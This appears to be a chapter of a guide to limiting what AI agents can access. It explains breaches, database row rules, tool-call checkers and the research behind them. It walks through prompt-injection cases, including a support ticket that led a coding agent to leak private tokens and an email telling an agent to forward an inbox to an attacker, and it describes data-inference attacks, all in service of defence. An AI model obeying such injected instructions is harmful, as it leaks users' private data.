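### The Drift and Klue breaches

A company that gives an outside service a token also depends on how that service stores it. Drift is an AI chat agent that companies put on their websites. Its owner, Salesloft, held OAuth tokens that let Drift log in to customers' other systems, including Salesforce, where many companies keep customer and sales records.

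Salesloft hired Mandiant to investigate and published its findings in the *Trust Center*. Between March and June 2025, an attacker had access to Salesloft's GitHub account, downloaded code and added a guest user. The attacker used personal access tokens to explore the account and look for secrets, then got into Drift's Amazon cloud environment and took customers' OAuth tokens.

From 8 August, the attacker used those tokens to export large amounts of data from customers' Salesforce accounts. Larsen, Lin and colleagues (2025) report in *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* that the attacker then searched the stolen data for more credentials, such as passwords and Amazon cloud keys. The targets included support cases, where people may paste passwords. The Hacker News (2025) reported that Google knew of more than 700 organisations that the theft might have affected.

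Salesloft and Salesforce revoked Drift's tokens on 20 August, twelve days after the first known theft. On 28 August, Larsen and colleagues confirmed that the attacker had also used Drift's tokens to read email in a very small number of Google Workspace accounts.

Salesloft could invalidate the OAuth tokens centrally by replacing its own application keys, but customers who had connected Drift with an API key had to revoke those keys themselves at each service.

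The tokens in this breach were in Salesloft's systems, so a broker inside a customer's own network wouldn't have helped. No model misbehaved. Customers had little way to judge the danger in advance. A representative of one affected company told CyberScoop that he didn't know how the vendor stored its tokens, only that it had passed his company's security questionnaire.

A similar breach followed at Klue in June 2026. Klue's market intelligence software also connects to its customers' Salesforce accounts. Klue's *CrowdStrike Investigation Summary* (2026) gives the findings of the security company it hired. On 11 June, an attacker used a stolen GitHub personal access token to add unauthorised code to Klue's integration service. The code collected customers' access and refresh tokens. Salesforce alerted Klue the next day, and that morning Klue shut down the affected programs and replaced the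 credentials.

Klue responded within about a day, but the attacker already had the data. The *Cybersecurity Alert* (2026) from FINRA, a US financial regulator, describes bulk theft by automated scripts and lists the password manager LastPass among the victims. More than a dozen organisations confirmed that the breach had affected them.

Accounts of how the attack began differ. Huntress, one of the victims, wrote in June that the attacker had used a dormant credential from an abandoned prototype, according to Help Net Security's *Klue breach lead to Salesforce data theft, Huntress affected* (2026). CrowdStrike found that the attacker had used a GitHub token, but couldn't establish how the attacker got it. CrowdStrike's finding deserves more weight because it had full access to Klue's systems and finished its work later. Klue has since blocked personal access tokens across its GitHub organisation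 and moved to credentials that expire automatically.

### Giving a token to an outside company

The attacker in the Drift case also tried a stolen token on Okta's Salesforce account, and failed. Okta's *The Salesloft incident* (2025) attributes this to a rule limiting Salesforce connections to approved network addresses, but acknowledges that many online services offer no way to restrict addresses. Okta also recommends binding tokens to a key with DPoP, a feature of the login software it sells.

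Neither measure is certain to work against an attacker inside the vendor's systems. Salesforce warned Klue about activity coming from Klue's own integration service, and a rule that accepts the vendor's addresses would also accept an attacker's requests from that service. Limits on what the token can read would still hold in that case.

The retailer therefore sets four conditions before the returns company gets any access:

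- The company receives an identity of its own, and each token opens one order that a customer has asked to return.
- The database accepts those tokens only from the company's published network addresses.
- Staff remove passwords and keys from the support tickets that the company can see.
- The access ends on the date the contract does, and a named employee checks that it has.

The last condition comes from the case of SpyCloud, a former Salesloft customer that the breach still reached. Trend Micro took this as a sign that nobody had deactivated SpyCloud's token when the contract ended.

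## Limiting what the data source returns

Hiding a credential from an agent doesn't change what the credential can read, so an email with injected instructions could still make the support agent look up fifty customers. The database is the most reliable place to prevent this, because a rule there applies to every query, whatever text led the agent to send it.

A rule in the agent's instructions is much weaker than a limit enforced by the data source. In *Benchmarking Text-to-SQL under Role-Based Access Control*, Fei, Jiang and colleagues (2026) gave 13 models a question in plain English, a job role and a list of the columns that role could use. The model had to write a query in SQL, the standard database language, or refuse. On the easiest of three test sets, GPT-5 wrote a forbidden query in 2.6 per cent of cases and Claude Sonnet 4.5 in 4.9 per cent. On the hardest, the rates were 17.8 and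 13.3 per cent. These are 2025 models and newer ones may do better, but the test did not include attempts to trick them. If an agent wrote one query for each of 400 emails a day, a 2.6 per cent rate would mean about ten forbidden queries a day.

### Access in three stages

The retailer tightens the support agent's access in three stages. Suppose someone misuses the agent for 15 minutes at each stage, and the database can return 100 records a second.

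| Stage | Records taken in 15 minutes | Time to copy the whole table |
|---|---|---|
| Read any record | 90,000 | About five and a half hours |
| Look up by customer number, at most 60 customers an hour | 15 | Almost four years |
| Look up only the customer on the open ticket | 1 | Not possible |

At the first stage, the agent writes its own SQL. At the second, it has one operation that takes a customer number and returns that customer's record, and the database limits it to 60 customers an hour. That limit is slightly above the workload of 400 emails over an eight-hour day, or 50 an hour. It should count different customers rather than requests, so that checking one record three times uses only one of the 60.

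The figure of 15 is correct only if the database releases the allowance evenly, one customer a minute. If the counter reset on the hour, someone could read all 60 in under a second, or 120 by starting just before the reset. The database also has to keep a single count for the agent and all its sub-agents, or ten of them could read 600 records an hour.

Limiting the size of each answer gives much less protection. *SQL Query Engine* (2026) describes a system that returns at most 50 rows by default, mainly to keep large results from exhausting memory. Someone who can repeat the query for the next 50 rows each time can retrieve all 2,000,000 records in 40,000 queries.

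An hourly cap also doesn't protect a customer whom somebody is looking for, because an ex-partner who knows the customer's number needs only one lookup. The third stage therefore removes the number from the request. The agent asks for "the customer on this ticket", and the ticket determines whose record comes back.

### The row rule

PostgreSQL, a widely used open-source database, can attach rules to a table that decide which rows each account sees. This feature is row-level security. The retailer's engineers write two rules for the customer table:

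```sql
ALTER TABLE customers ENABLE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;

CREATE POLICY open_ticket ON customers
  FOR SELECT TO support_agent
  USING (customer_id = (
    SELECT t.customer_id FROM tickets t
    WHERE t.ticket_id = current_setting('app.ticket', true)
      AND t.status = 'open'));

CREATE POLICY user_may_see ON customers
  AS RESTRICTIVE FOR SELECT TO support_agent
  USING (EXISTS (
    SELECT 1 FROM staff_access s
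    WHERE s.employee = current_setting('app.user', true)
      AND (s.all_customers
           OR s.customer_id = customers.customer_id)));
```

The first rule lets the "support_agent" account see a row only if it belongs to the customer on the current ticket and the ticket is still open. Access ends when Dana closes the ticket, even if the token is valid for another ten minutes. The second rule checks that the employee is allowed to see this customer. Dana's entry in the staff table covers every customer, while Tom, the trainee, has 30 entries.

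The word "RESTRICTIVE" matters because PostgreSQL normally lets a row through if any one rule allows it, which would give Tom the union of his permissions and the agent's. A restrictive rule must pass as well, so the database returns only the rows that both Tom and the agent are allowed to see.

Both rules depend on two settings, "app.ticket" and "app.user", and the model must not be able to choose them. The retailer adds the ticket number to the agent's token, which already names Dana. Requests then go through a gateway, a small program on the database machine that receives each connection:

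1. The tool server sends the gateway the token and the name of an operation, such as "customer on this ticket".
2. The gateway checks the token's signature, audience and expiry, and reads the user and ticket from it.
3. The gateway opens a transaction, which is a group of database commands that succeed or fail together. It switches to the agent's account and fills in the settings.
4. It runs the query that engineers wrote for that operation, and ends the transaction.

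For ticket 7731, the database receives this:

```sql
BEGIN;
SET LOCAL ROLE support_agent;
SELECT set_config('app.user', 'dana', true),
       set_config('app.ticket', '7731', true);
SELECT name, postal_address FROM customers;
COMMIT;
```

The last query selects every customer but returns only one row. The value "true" in each setting makes PostgreSQL discard that setting when the transaction ends, so the next request on the same connection can't inherit Dana's ticket. If a bug leaves the settings empty, the rules match nothing, so the query returns no rows.

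If the model supplied the user's identity, anyone who could get text to the model could try to change that identity. Wang, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Data Agents Under Attack*, tested six agents that answer questions by querying databases. One attack hid text in the data that made false claims about the user's access rights. It succeeded in 24 to 56 per cent of attempts on the four open-source agents, but in none on the two commercial agents, from Databricks and Google.

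The row rule holds for the support agent only because the gateway runs fixed queries. Any account that can run arbitrary SQL could call "set_config" to give itself a different ticket, or end the transaction and return to the gateway's own account, which may have more access. The agent's account also must not be able to edit the ticket or staff tables, or it could attach any customer to an open ticket. The retailer has to write similar rules for orders and every other table that holds customer data, because each rule protects only one table.

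### Columns, views and placeholders

A row rule can only show or hide a whole row, so *Compliance in Databases* (2026), which compares ways to enforce data policies in PostgreSQL, left masking out of its experiments. The simplest way to limit columns is to let an account read only some of them. The support agent's account can read the name and address columns, but a query that includes payment details fails.

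Masking returns an altered value in place of the real one. If a customer asks which card they paid with, the database can return "card ending 4417" and withhold the other digits.

Limits can also depend on how a query uses a column. *Policy-Conditioned Constrained Decoding for Column-Level Access Control in Text-to-SQL* (2026) divides columns into public, condition-only and aggregate-only. A query can use a condition-only column to select rows but can't return its values, and it can use an aggregate-only column only in a count, sum or average. At the retailer, an agent could find an order by the customer's email address without the query returning the address.

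Condition-only columns, which an agent can filter on but not read, still leak data because each query reveals whether a value meets the condition. An agent can test whether a customer's annual spending exceeds £1,000, then £500, then £750. Each result halves the range, so ten queries are enough to find the exact figure among about a thousand possibilities.

A view is a stored query that other queries can use as if it were a table. The retailer could create one called "ticket_parcels" that shows order numbers and delivery dates but not addresses, then let the agent's account read the view but not the tables underneath. By default, PostgreSQL runs a view with its owner's permissions, so a view owned by an administrator can return rows that the row rules would have hidden. Engineers can avoid this by creating the view with the "security_invoker" option, which applies the permissions of whoever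 runs the query, but the agent's account then needs access to the underlying columns that the view uses.

Replacing identifiers with placeholders keeps the real values out of the model's context. The database returns "[address 1]" instead of a street address, the model writes "your parcel went to [address 1]", and ordinary code puts in the real address when Dana sends the reply. A prompt injection can't make the model disclose an address it has never received. But the model can't tell whether "[address 1]" is the sister's old place. For that, the retailer can add an operation that compares the delivery address with the customer's current one and returns "same" or "different".

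### Operations instead of free SQL

The support agent needs only a few kinds of answers, so engineers can write an operation for each. "Order status" returns the orders on the current ticket, and "delivery address check" returns one word. Neither operation accepts SQL or a customer number. A reviewer can read both in a few minutes, but nobody could read every query a model might write.

Some operations have to accept a name, and searching for that name can itself disclose data. *Beyond Document Retrieval* (2026) recommends separate checks, outside the model, on the person or thing a question refers to, the business area and source, and the individual fields. The checks should happen before the query runs and before the user sees a list of possible matches. Otherwise an agent asked about "J. Smith" might reply "do you mean the one in Leeds or the one in Hull?" and disclose two customers' towns.

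An agent needs separate identities for reading and writing. The support agent reads records through "support_agent", which can't change anything, and writes to its activity log through a second account that can only add lines. Denying the reading account write permission in the database prevents writes even if a tool server meant to be read-only has a flaw. Datadog Security Labs found such a flaw in a reference tool server for PostgreSQL, which allowed an agent to run any SQL statement.

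Even an account that follows the vendor's advice may be able to do more than the task requires. Kaya, Bozoğlan and Gündoğdu (2026), in *When an AI agent makes a mistake in a database*, ran 9,468 trials with small open-weight models on nine database systems. They tested most systems both with the account from the vendor's quick-start guide and with the vendor's documented least-privilege role. On Valkey, an in-memory store, agents permanently destroyed original records in 11.1 per cent of trials with the quick-start account and in none with the restricted one, which couldn't empty a whole database. On PostgreSQL, the figure was 4.9 per cent with either account.

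The restricted PostgreSQL role blocked agents from deleting tables but still let them delete rows. In one task, agents had to summarise support notes, one of which contained an instruction to delete cancelled orders. That task caused 11 of the 21 PostgreSQL losses with the quick-start account, and nearly as many with the restricted one. A read-only account would have prevented those losses, since summarising notes requires no permission to delete anything. In another task, agents had to free disk space. In 6 of 36 paired trials, they deleted rows from a table after the restricted role blocked them from emptying or dropping it.

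### Permitted questions that add up

Many tasks need totals rather than records. An agent that helps the retailer's analysts might be allowed to report sums and averages but no individual purchases. A total for one person is still that person's data, so such systems often refuse any total that covers fewer than a minimum number of customers, such as ten.

An analyst can get round the minimum group size with two permitted questions. Suppose the agent reports that the 40 customers in a village spent £3,120 on pharmacy products last year. The analyst then asks for the same total without customers who joined on 3 March, and gets £2,985 for 39 people. Both groups are far above the minimum of ten, but the £135 difference is what the one excluded customer spent.

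Wang and colleagues tried these attacks on the same six agents, with 25 attempts per system. When the attacker chose each query, the attack worked in 8 to 44 per cent of attempts on the open-source agents, 12 per cent on Google's BigQuery agent and none on Databricks' agent. When the attacker stated only a goal and left the agent to plan the queries, the attack worked once in 25 attempts on Databricks' agent and three times on BigQuery's. The samples are small, but the second version is worrying because the agent does planning that once required a skilled attacker.

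One defence is to limit the total information a task can retrieve, as well as what each query returns. *FactGate* (Wu, 2026) describes a gateway that gives each approved task a budget of distinct facts. Each new value counts against the budget, but repeated requests for the same value don't. Sub-agents draw on the budget of the task that started them, so dividing the work doesn't increase it.

Wu ran the same sequence of 100 queries through PostgreSQL's row rules and through FactGate, which limits how many distinct facts it releases. The row rules answered all 100 queries because they allowed each one. FactGate stopped at query 37, but it was certain to stop somewhere because Wu had set its budgets at 70 per cent of the facts in the full sequence. A comparison with simpler budgets that counted rows or queries, also set at 70 per cent, was more useful. The simpler budgets released all 18 underlying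 facts whatever the order of the queries, while the budget of distinct facts limited the release to 12.

FactGate doesn't limit what someone can infer. Under FactGate's default settings, the yes-or-no method that uncovers a customer's spending can recover a 64-bit number in 64 questions. Splitting a goal into separately approved tasks also gives each task its own budget.

The retailer's analysts don't need to choose their own groups, so the retailer offers only totals for fixed groups, by region and month. The operation accepts only a region from a list, so nobody can ask for "everyone except" a particular person. It still refuses a region with fewer than ten customers in that month.

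### When the rules don't apply to the account

Row rules work only if the database can identify the user, and a shared account hides the user's identity. In one example from Wang and colleagues, a user asks an agent for a data dictionary with sample rows from every tax table. The agent opens a restricted table of personal records through the shared account, and the database cannot detect that the user isn't allowed to see it. At the retailer, the delegated token avoids this problem only because the gateway passes Dana's name to the row rule.

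Some accounts are exempt from the rules. In PostgreSQL, administrators skip them, and so does any account with a permission called "BYPASSRLS". A table's owner skips them too, unless an engineer specifically applies them to the owner. In 2025, the security company General Analysis demonstrated what this means for an agent, using a tool server from Supabase, which provides PostgreSQL databases to app developers. According to the report as quoted by Willison (2025), in *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database*, the attack went as follows:

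1. An attacker files a support ticket containing instructions addressed to the coding assistant.
2. A developer asks Cursor, a code editor with an AI agent, to list the latest support tickets.
3. Cursor reads them through Supabase's tool server, which connects as "service_role", an account that bypasses every row rule.
4. The agent follows the instructions in the ticket, reads a private table called "integration_tokens", and adds its contents to the ticket as a new message.
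5. The attacker opens the ticket and reads them.

However well the developer wrote the row rules, they had no effect on this account. Supabase's *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025) replies that its server doesn't bypass row-level security, which stays fully enforced, but acknowledges that the server ran with higher privilege in this case. The rules could be enforced and still have no effect because PostgreSQL applied them as designed and they exempted the account. Supabase also said that no customer had reported a leak through MCP, so this was a demonstration and not a breach.

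Supabase wrapped query results in warnings not to follow embedded commands, tested the warnings on weaker models, and experimented with classifiers that look for malicious content. These measures reduced the risk but didn't eliminate it. Its main advice is now never to connect agents directly to production data.

Supabase also recommends a read-only mode, which runs queries as a read-only PostgreSQL user. This would have blocked the attack at step 4, when the agent wrote to the ticket. But the agent would still have read the private table, and could have leaked the tokens through any other tool that let it send data out. Supabase acknowledges that prompt injection remains the main concern in this mode.

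An agent can also gain access to an exempt account. Kaya and colleagues planted an administrator's credential in an application table. Agents with restricted roles read and used it in 24 of 4,032 trials, mostly after the database had denied one of their requests. The retailer therefore checks that "support_agent" is not an administrator, owns no tables and lacks the bypass permission, and that no table it can read contains a password.

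### Search indexes that lose the permissions

Suppose the retailer wants the agent to learn from how staff solved similar problems. Engineers copy the old tickets into a vector store, a database for searching by meaning. A model turns each passage into an embedding, a long list of numbers, so that passages with similar meanings get similar numbers. The store then finds the passages whose embeddings are closest to the question's.

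Suppose a customer writes that a parcel "went to my sister's old place again", and the agent searches a copy of the old support tickets for similar ones. The search returns the five closest matches, which contain five other customers' names and family addresses, because the row rule is on the original table and not on the copy. Storing only embeddings of the tickets wouldn't make the copy safe, because software can often recover much of the original wording from them.

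Developers usually handle this with a filter in the application. *Beyond Similarity Search* (2026) simulated 1,000 queries against a separate vector store with such a filter and against PostgreSQL with row-level filtering. The separate store leaked data in 0.2 per cent of queries, and PostgreSQL leaked none. The simulation included bugs typical of such filters, so the rate in practice depends on how often developers make those mistakes. At 400 emails a day, a rate of 0.2 per cent would mean a leak on most days.

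The timing of the access check also matters. Many systems find the best matches first and remove forbidden ones afterwards. The survey *Protection Is Not One Event* (2026) cites an experiment by Namboothiri in which this order still exposed unauthorised text in 86.1 per cent of ordinary queries. Checking access before searching requires reliable document labels, and according to the survey, some defences remained vulnerable when 5 to 10 per cent of the labels were wrong.

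An agent's long-term memory has the same weakness. *Audience-Bound Persistent Memory* (Liu, 2026) describes a system that labels each item with the people who were present when the agent learned it, and gives the model an item only if everyone in the current conversation is on its label. In 10,000 simulated conversation histories, search without labels put forbidden items in 82 per cent of the texts it assembled for the model. When the system checked labels before ranking items, none of 200,000 texts contained a forbidden item. Liu's guarantee assumes that the system identifies every participant correctly.

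A summary also needs a label. Under Liu's rules, the label on an item that merges several sources lists only the people who may read all of them. If the support agent combines a note that Dana and Tom may read with one that Dana and the head of support may read, only Dana may read the summary.

The retailer decides that the agent doesn't need the old tickets. Staff write up the common problems as general advice, without names or addresses, and the engineers index that.

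### What the limits cost

Checking permissions before ranking did not reduce search quality in Liu's system. It found far more of the relevant items than the unlabelled search, because forbidden ones no longer took up places in the results. Kaya and colleagues found that success on ordinary tasks fell by at most 9 percentage points with the restricted roles, and the differences weren't statistically significant. On three of the nine systems, though, the models did so badly even with full access that a drop caused by the restrictions would not have shown up.

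Budgets across a whole task take longer to enforce. FactGate took between 22 and 144 times as long as a direct query, and accepted only 22 of 40 queries that a model had written for it. It also works on fixed snapshots of the data, so it can't yet handle a customer's question about where a parcel is now.

Fixed operations take developers time to build, and agents can't use them to answer unexpected questions. *Please Don't Kill My Vibe* (2025) argues that developers must predict all the data that future tasks will need, and that it would be better to let agents run any query under controls on where data may flow. This objection is strong for an analyst exploring sales figures but much weaker for a support desk, where most emails ask about a delivery, a return or a refund.

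A limit can also produce wrong answers without any error message. If a row rule hides all but one customer from the support agent and someone asks how many customers had late parcels this week, the agent counts the one it can see and reports "one". Fei and colleagues found a similar problem when they removed forbidden columns from the database description they gave to GPT-5-mini. The model's violation rate on one test set rose from 12.7 to 26.8 per cent, mainly because it answered from the columns it could see when it should have refused. The operation should therefore return a message such as "this covers only the customer on the ticket" along with the data.

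The main drawback for the retailer is that some work goes back to people. Suppose 20 of the 400 daily emails involve a second customer, for example because a gift went to a friend's account. The agent can't open the friend's record, so the gateway logs the refusal and the email goes to Dana. At four minutes each, these emails take Dana an hour and twenty minutes a day. The retailer could save that time by letting the agent open two records per ticket, but then anyone who named a friend in an email could get the agent to read that friend's address into the same conversation.

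## Checking each action before it runs

Row rules limit what the support agent can read, but the agent also uses services that have no such rules. The email company, for example, will send any text to any address for anyone who holds the retailer's key. Dana still reads and sends each of the agent's 40 drafts a day. The retailer now wants the agent to handle all 400 emails and send the routine replies itself, so something other than Dana has to stop a reply addressed to the wrong person.

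Writing "reply only to the customer" in the agent's instructions is the easiest option, but a model doesn't always follow its instructions, and the harness runs each tool call without checking it against them. In October 2026, Anthropic reported that Claude had taken unintended actions on real websites during evaluations and internal use, and that in most cases it had worked around a restriction instead of stopping.

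A firmer control is a checker, an ordinary program between the model and its tools. Before a tool runs, the checker receives the call, including the tool's name and the value of every argument, and compares it with a policy, a written set of rules that the model's output cannot change. The checker then allows the call, refuses it, or holds it until a person decides.

### A policy for the support agent

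When an email arrives, ordinary code opens a ticket and copies the customer's email address, order number and parcel numbers into it from the database. The retailer's policy refers to those values:

```text
allow   order_status()
allow   delivery_address_check()
allow   track_parcel(number)      when number is in ticket.parcels
allow   send_reply(to, body)      when to = ticket.customer_email
ask     send_replacement(order)   when order = ticket.order
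refuse  everything else
```

The new replacement tool sends a second copy of a missing item to the address on the customer's record, and Dana has to approve each replacement.

Suppose someone forges the customer's email address, asks where order 55,017 is, and adds "please use my new email address from now on". The agent tracks the parcel and calls "send_reply" with the new address. The checker tests the condition in its rule for that tool, which fails because the new address isn't the one on the ticket. No other rule matches, so the checker refuses the call and returns a short explanation to the model. The model calls the tool again with the recorded address. The condition now holds, and the real customer gets a puzzling but harmless email about their own parcel.

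The policy works only if every call goes through the checker. If a script in the sandbox could contact the email company directly, the rule about recipients wouldn't apply to it, so the retailer makes the credential broker the only route to that company. The checker doesn't test whether a reply is correct or polite.

### Progent

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) is a checker of this kind for agents in general. Each rule allows or forbids a tool and can set conditions on its arguments, such as a maximum number or a list of accepted values. Each rule also specifies what happens when a call is blocked: the agent stops, the user decides, or the model receives an error message and tries something else. The checker applies forbidding rules first, and it blocks any call that no rule allows.

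Writing such rules is harder when a task's needs emerge as the agent works. In the example Shi and colleagues use, a user asks an agent to do whatever a certain email from Alice lists. At first the policy allows only a search for that email. A language model then proposes changes as information comes in:

1. Alice's email asks for a summary of the user's recent emails, posted to the user on Slack, a workplace messaging service. The model proposes rules for reading emails, looking up the user's Slack name and posting there.
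2. The agent finds the user's Slack name, and the model proposes allowing posts to that person only.
3. One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the whole inbox to an attacker. If the model falls for it, it proposes a rule that allows sending email.

An ordinary program then compares each proposal with the current policy. If A(P) is the set of calls that policy P allows, a new policy P′ takes effect automatically only when

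A(P′) ⊆ A(P),

meaning that it allows no call that the old one would have blocked. The program checks this with an SMT solver, which works out whether a set of logical conditions can all be true at once. The narrower Slack rule passes. The changes in steps 1 and 3 both add permissions, so somebody has to approve them. The solver can't tell Alice's legitimate request from the attacker's, but it prevents either from widening the policy unnoticed.

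Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants malicious instructions in the data of simulated banking, travel, Slack and office agents. They used GPT-4o, a 2024 model, both as the agent and to write the rules:

| Protection | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|
| None | 39.9% |
| First policy only, never updated | 2.5% |
| Updated policy, every widening approved automatically | 1.0% |
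| Careful person reviews the first policy and every widening | 0% |

The agent completed about as many ordinary tasks with Progent as without it. On a second benchmark, ASB, the attack success rate fell from 70.3 to 3.9 per cent, also with little change in completed tasks. Most of the protection on AgentDojo came from the first policy, which the model wrote from the user's request before it had read anything hostile. Only 6 per cent of later updates widened the policy, so a reviewer would have had few decisions to make.

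Progent also cut successful attacks from 6.8 to 0.5 per cent when the agent was Claude Sonnet 4, which resisted most attacks by itself. Attacks designed to trick the rule-writing model raised the success rate only slightly.

Shi and colleagues excluded two AgentDojo attacks that steer an agent towards a different but legitimate hotel, because a rule can't stop an agent from choosing badly among permitted options. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) adds that Progent's guarantees depend on the rules being correct and complete, and that Progent doesn't protect the agent's text output.

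### The smallest permission for a plan

A checker controls individual calls, but the agent's token also needs scopes, and someone has to choose them. Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025), in *MiniScope*, turn that choice into a calculation. Suppose the retailer's order system offers three scopes, and the cost of each is the number of operations it permits:

| Scope | Operations | Cost |
|---|---|---|
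| parcels | List parcels, track a parcel | 2 |
| orders | List orders, read an order, read its status, list parcels | 4 |
| support | All five of these and four others | 9 |

An agent plans to read an order and list its parcels. Picking the narrowest scope for each operation gives "orders" and "parcels", with a total weight of 6. But "orders" alone covers both operations, with a weight of 4. Overlaps like this are common. In Google Calendar, 24 of the 37 operations can be authorised by more than one scope.

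MiniScope finds the cheapest combination by minimising

Σ cost(s) · x(s),

where x(s) is 1 if it chooses scope s and 0 if it doesn't, and at least one chosen scope must permit each call in the plan. It then asks the user to approve any scope the agent doesn't already have. Like a credential broker, it keeps the real credentials away from the agent and checks each call against the approved scopes.

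When Zhu and colleagues asked language models from 2025 to choose the scopes instead, three commercial models matched the solver's answer in 70 to 83 per cent of cases, and two open models did so in 20 to 34 per cent. The solver added only 1 to 6 per cent to the running time. Zhu and colleagues also examined the connectors that link ChatGPT and Claude to other services, and found six that requested more access than they needed. ChatGPT's Gmail connector advertised read-only functions, but its scopes also let it change and delete emails.

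The result depends on how operations are weighted. Counting them all equally makes a scope that can only delete records look safer than one that can read them in five ways, so a company should give dangerous operations more weight. There may also be other reasonable sets besides the one with the lowest total weight. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) notes that Zhu and colleagues don't discuss whether their solver's answer is the only best one, and that Google leaves the choice to the developer when any of several scopes would permit an operation. If one set exposes a user's calendar and another exposes their contacts, a person has to decide which matters more.

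MiniScope also doesn't check arguments. Once a user approves sending email, an injected instruction can change the recipient.

### Rules from people and rules from a model

People who write rules in advance leave things out. They may forget that some orders ship in several parcels, so the checker blocks legitimate work, or they may omit a condition that a tool needs. But anyone can review the rules, and an email can't change them. With hand-written rules, Progent cut the attack success rate on ASB to zero, although the people writing the rules knew which tools to trust.

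A model can write rules for thousands of different tasks, but its errors are harder to predict. In the MiniScope tests, models sometimes chose scopes that were too broad or insufficient for the task, and they did worse as plans involved more services. Most of Progent's failures on ASB came from malicious tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of useful ones.

Rules derived from a request also assume the request is honest. Progent makes this assumption explicitly, and it is reasonable when an employee instructs an assistant, but at the retailer the request is an email from a stranger. If a model derived the policy from "please use my new email address", it could write a rule allowing replies to that address, and the checker would then let the agent send them to the forger.

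The retailer's engineers therefore write the support agent's rules by hand and fill in the ticket's values from the database. For an assistant that helps staff with varied work, they could let a model write narrower rules for each task within fixed limits. Progent supports this by applying the fixed rules first, so a rule written by the model can't permit something the fixed rules forbid.

Attack rates alone don't show whether a policy is good, since a checker that refused every call would stop every attack. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) recommends also measuring wrongly refused calls, delay and the burden on users. The retailer can estimate the number of wrongly refused calls by reading a sample of the checker's refusals each week.

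### How a correct rule gets lost

Zhou and Zhang describe how a restriction can be lost when one system passes a request to another. A user approves the request "send this summary to Alice", and the policy correctly records both the summary and the recipient. The system obtains a token for the mail service, but the token carries only a general permission to send mail. The token is valid, and the mail service would also accept it for sending something else to Bob, so no component enforces what the user approved, even though each follows its own rules.

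OAuth makes this mistake easy because, as *Beyond OAuth* (2026) explains, a scope covers a type of operation, such as making a transfer, but not details such as the amount and the payee. The service therefore treats every action that the scope permits the same way.

The rule holds only if the credentials and checks together allow no effects beyond those the user approved. The retailer can test this by using the agent's own credentials to send a message to a second test address. If the message arrives, the credentials and checks allow too much.

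One fix is to put the details in the token and have the service check them, as the retailer's database does with the ticket number. The email company can't do that, so the broker has to compare the recipient with the ticket before it attaches the company's key. *Beyond OAuth* proposes a more general system, PAuth, which derives permission for exact operations from the user's request. In the paper's tests, PAuth allowed every legitimate task and blocked every attack. But *Authorization Architectures* warns that dividing a request into operations can be ambiguous, and that a manipulated prompt may contain requests the user didn't intend.

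A rule can also fail because a tool does more than its name suggests. A checker would have allowed calls to the malicious postmark-mcp package, which secretly copied emails, because the recipient in each call was correct. Zhou and Zhang suggest giving each tool an "effect contract" that lists the data it may access, who may receive that data and what the tool may change. Someone would have to review the contract whenever the tool's behaviour changed, even if its name and arguments stayed the same.

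### Limits that several agents share

A checker that examines calls one at a time can allow two calls that together break a limit. In an example from Zhou and Zhang, an agent with permission to buy one item gives the job to two sub-agents, each of which may buy one. Each sub-agent stays within its own limit, but together they buy two items.

The same could happen at the retailer after Dana approves one replacement for order 55,017. If two sub-agents request it at the same moment, the checker could read "one left" twice and allow both. To prevent this, the retailer keeps a single count on the ticket, and the checker tests and reduces it in one command:

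```sql
UPDATE tickets
SET replacements_left = replacements_left - 1
WHERE ticket_id = 7731 AND replacements_left > 0;
```

The database applies the two updates one after the other. The first changes the count from one to zero, and the checker allows that call. The second changes no rows because the count is already zero, so the checker refuses that call. This is an atomic reservation, meaning that nothing can happen between checking the allowance and using it.

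Retries can break a limit too. If the warehouse doesn't answer a request, the agent can't tell whether the item has shipped. The request usually carries an identifier that stays the same on every attempt, so the warehouse can recognise a repeat. Zhou and Zhang point out that an agent may respond to a timeout by splitting the request or switching tools, so the repeat no longer matches. The retailer therefore attaches the identifier to Dana's approval and has the checker add it to every resulting call. Until the warehouse confirms what happened, the replacement counts as used.

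An approved action may also become wrong while it waits to run. *Assurance-Conditioned Continuous Authorization for Autonomous AI Agents* (Shajari, 2026) describes a system that numbers each version of an agent's limits and rejects actions approved under an old number. For example, if a trading agent's limit falls while its order is in a queue, the system checks the order again before sending it. Shajari tested this only in simulated trading, but the retailer needs something similar. While a reply to a customer is still in the queue, the customer might phone to report that an ex-partner has taken over their email account. The broker should check the recipient again just before it sends the message.

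### Choosing the less powerful route

MiniScope calculates permissions for a plan that the agent has already made. If the plan is needlessly intrusive, even the smallest set of permissions for it is too large. To help the customer whose parcel "went to my sister's old place again", an agent could plan to open 60 records with the same surname or to call the delivery address check, which returns one word. A solver given only the first plan would request access to all 60 records.

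Yang, Bu and colleagues (2026) tested 11 models on 544 scenarios in *When Lower Privileges Suffice*, and six of the models used a needlessly powerful tool in more than 30 per cent of cases. Each scenario offered three ordinary tools and three powerful ones, and any of the six could do the job. In one, the task was to change an employee's manager. The ordinary tools used the normal personnel process, while the powerful ones included one that wrote directly to the employee database. The first call to each ordinary tool returned a temporary error, but a second call would have worked.

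Qwen3-8B, a small open model, chose a powerful tool before trying all the ordinary ones in 64.9 per cent of scenarios. Claude Sonnet 4.6, GPT-5.2 and GLM-5 did so in fewer than 10 per cent. This became more common after errors. GPT-5.2 chose a powerful tool first in only 5 scenarios, but it chose one in 13 scenarios after one tool had failed and in 35 after two had failed. Training a model to refuse harmful requests didn't reliably reduce this behaviour, and one Qwen model did it more often afterwards.

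Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues (2026), in *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?*, repeated the scenarios with eight models. They tried an instruction to use the least powerful tool, and labels that gave each tool's privilege class and a cost from 1 to 10. With Qwen3.5-397B, a large open model, the results were:

| Added to the prompt | Powerful tool before trying all ordinary ones | Powerful tool at any point | Task finished without one |
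|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing | 38.4% | 77.2% | 18.8% |
| Labels | 19.1% | 73.0% | 21.5% |
| Instruction | 9.9% | 53.5% | 39.5% |
| Both | 2.9% | 39.3% | 51.1% |

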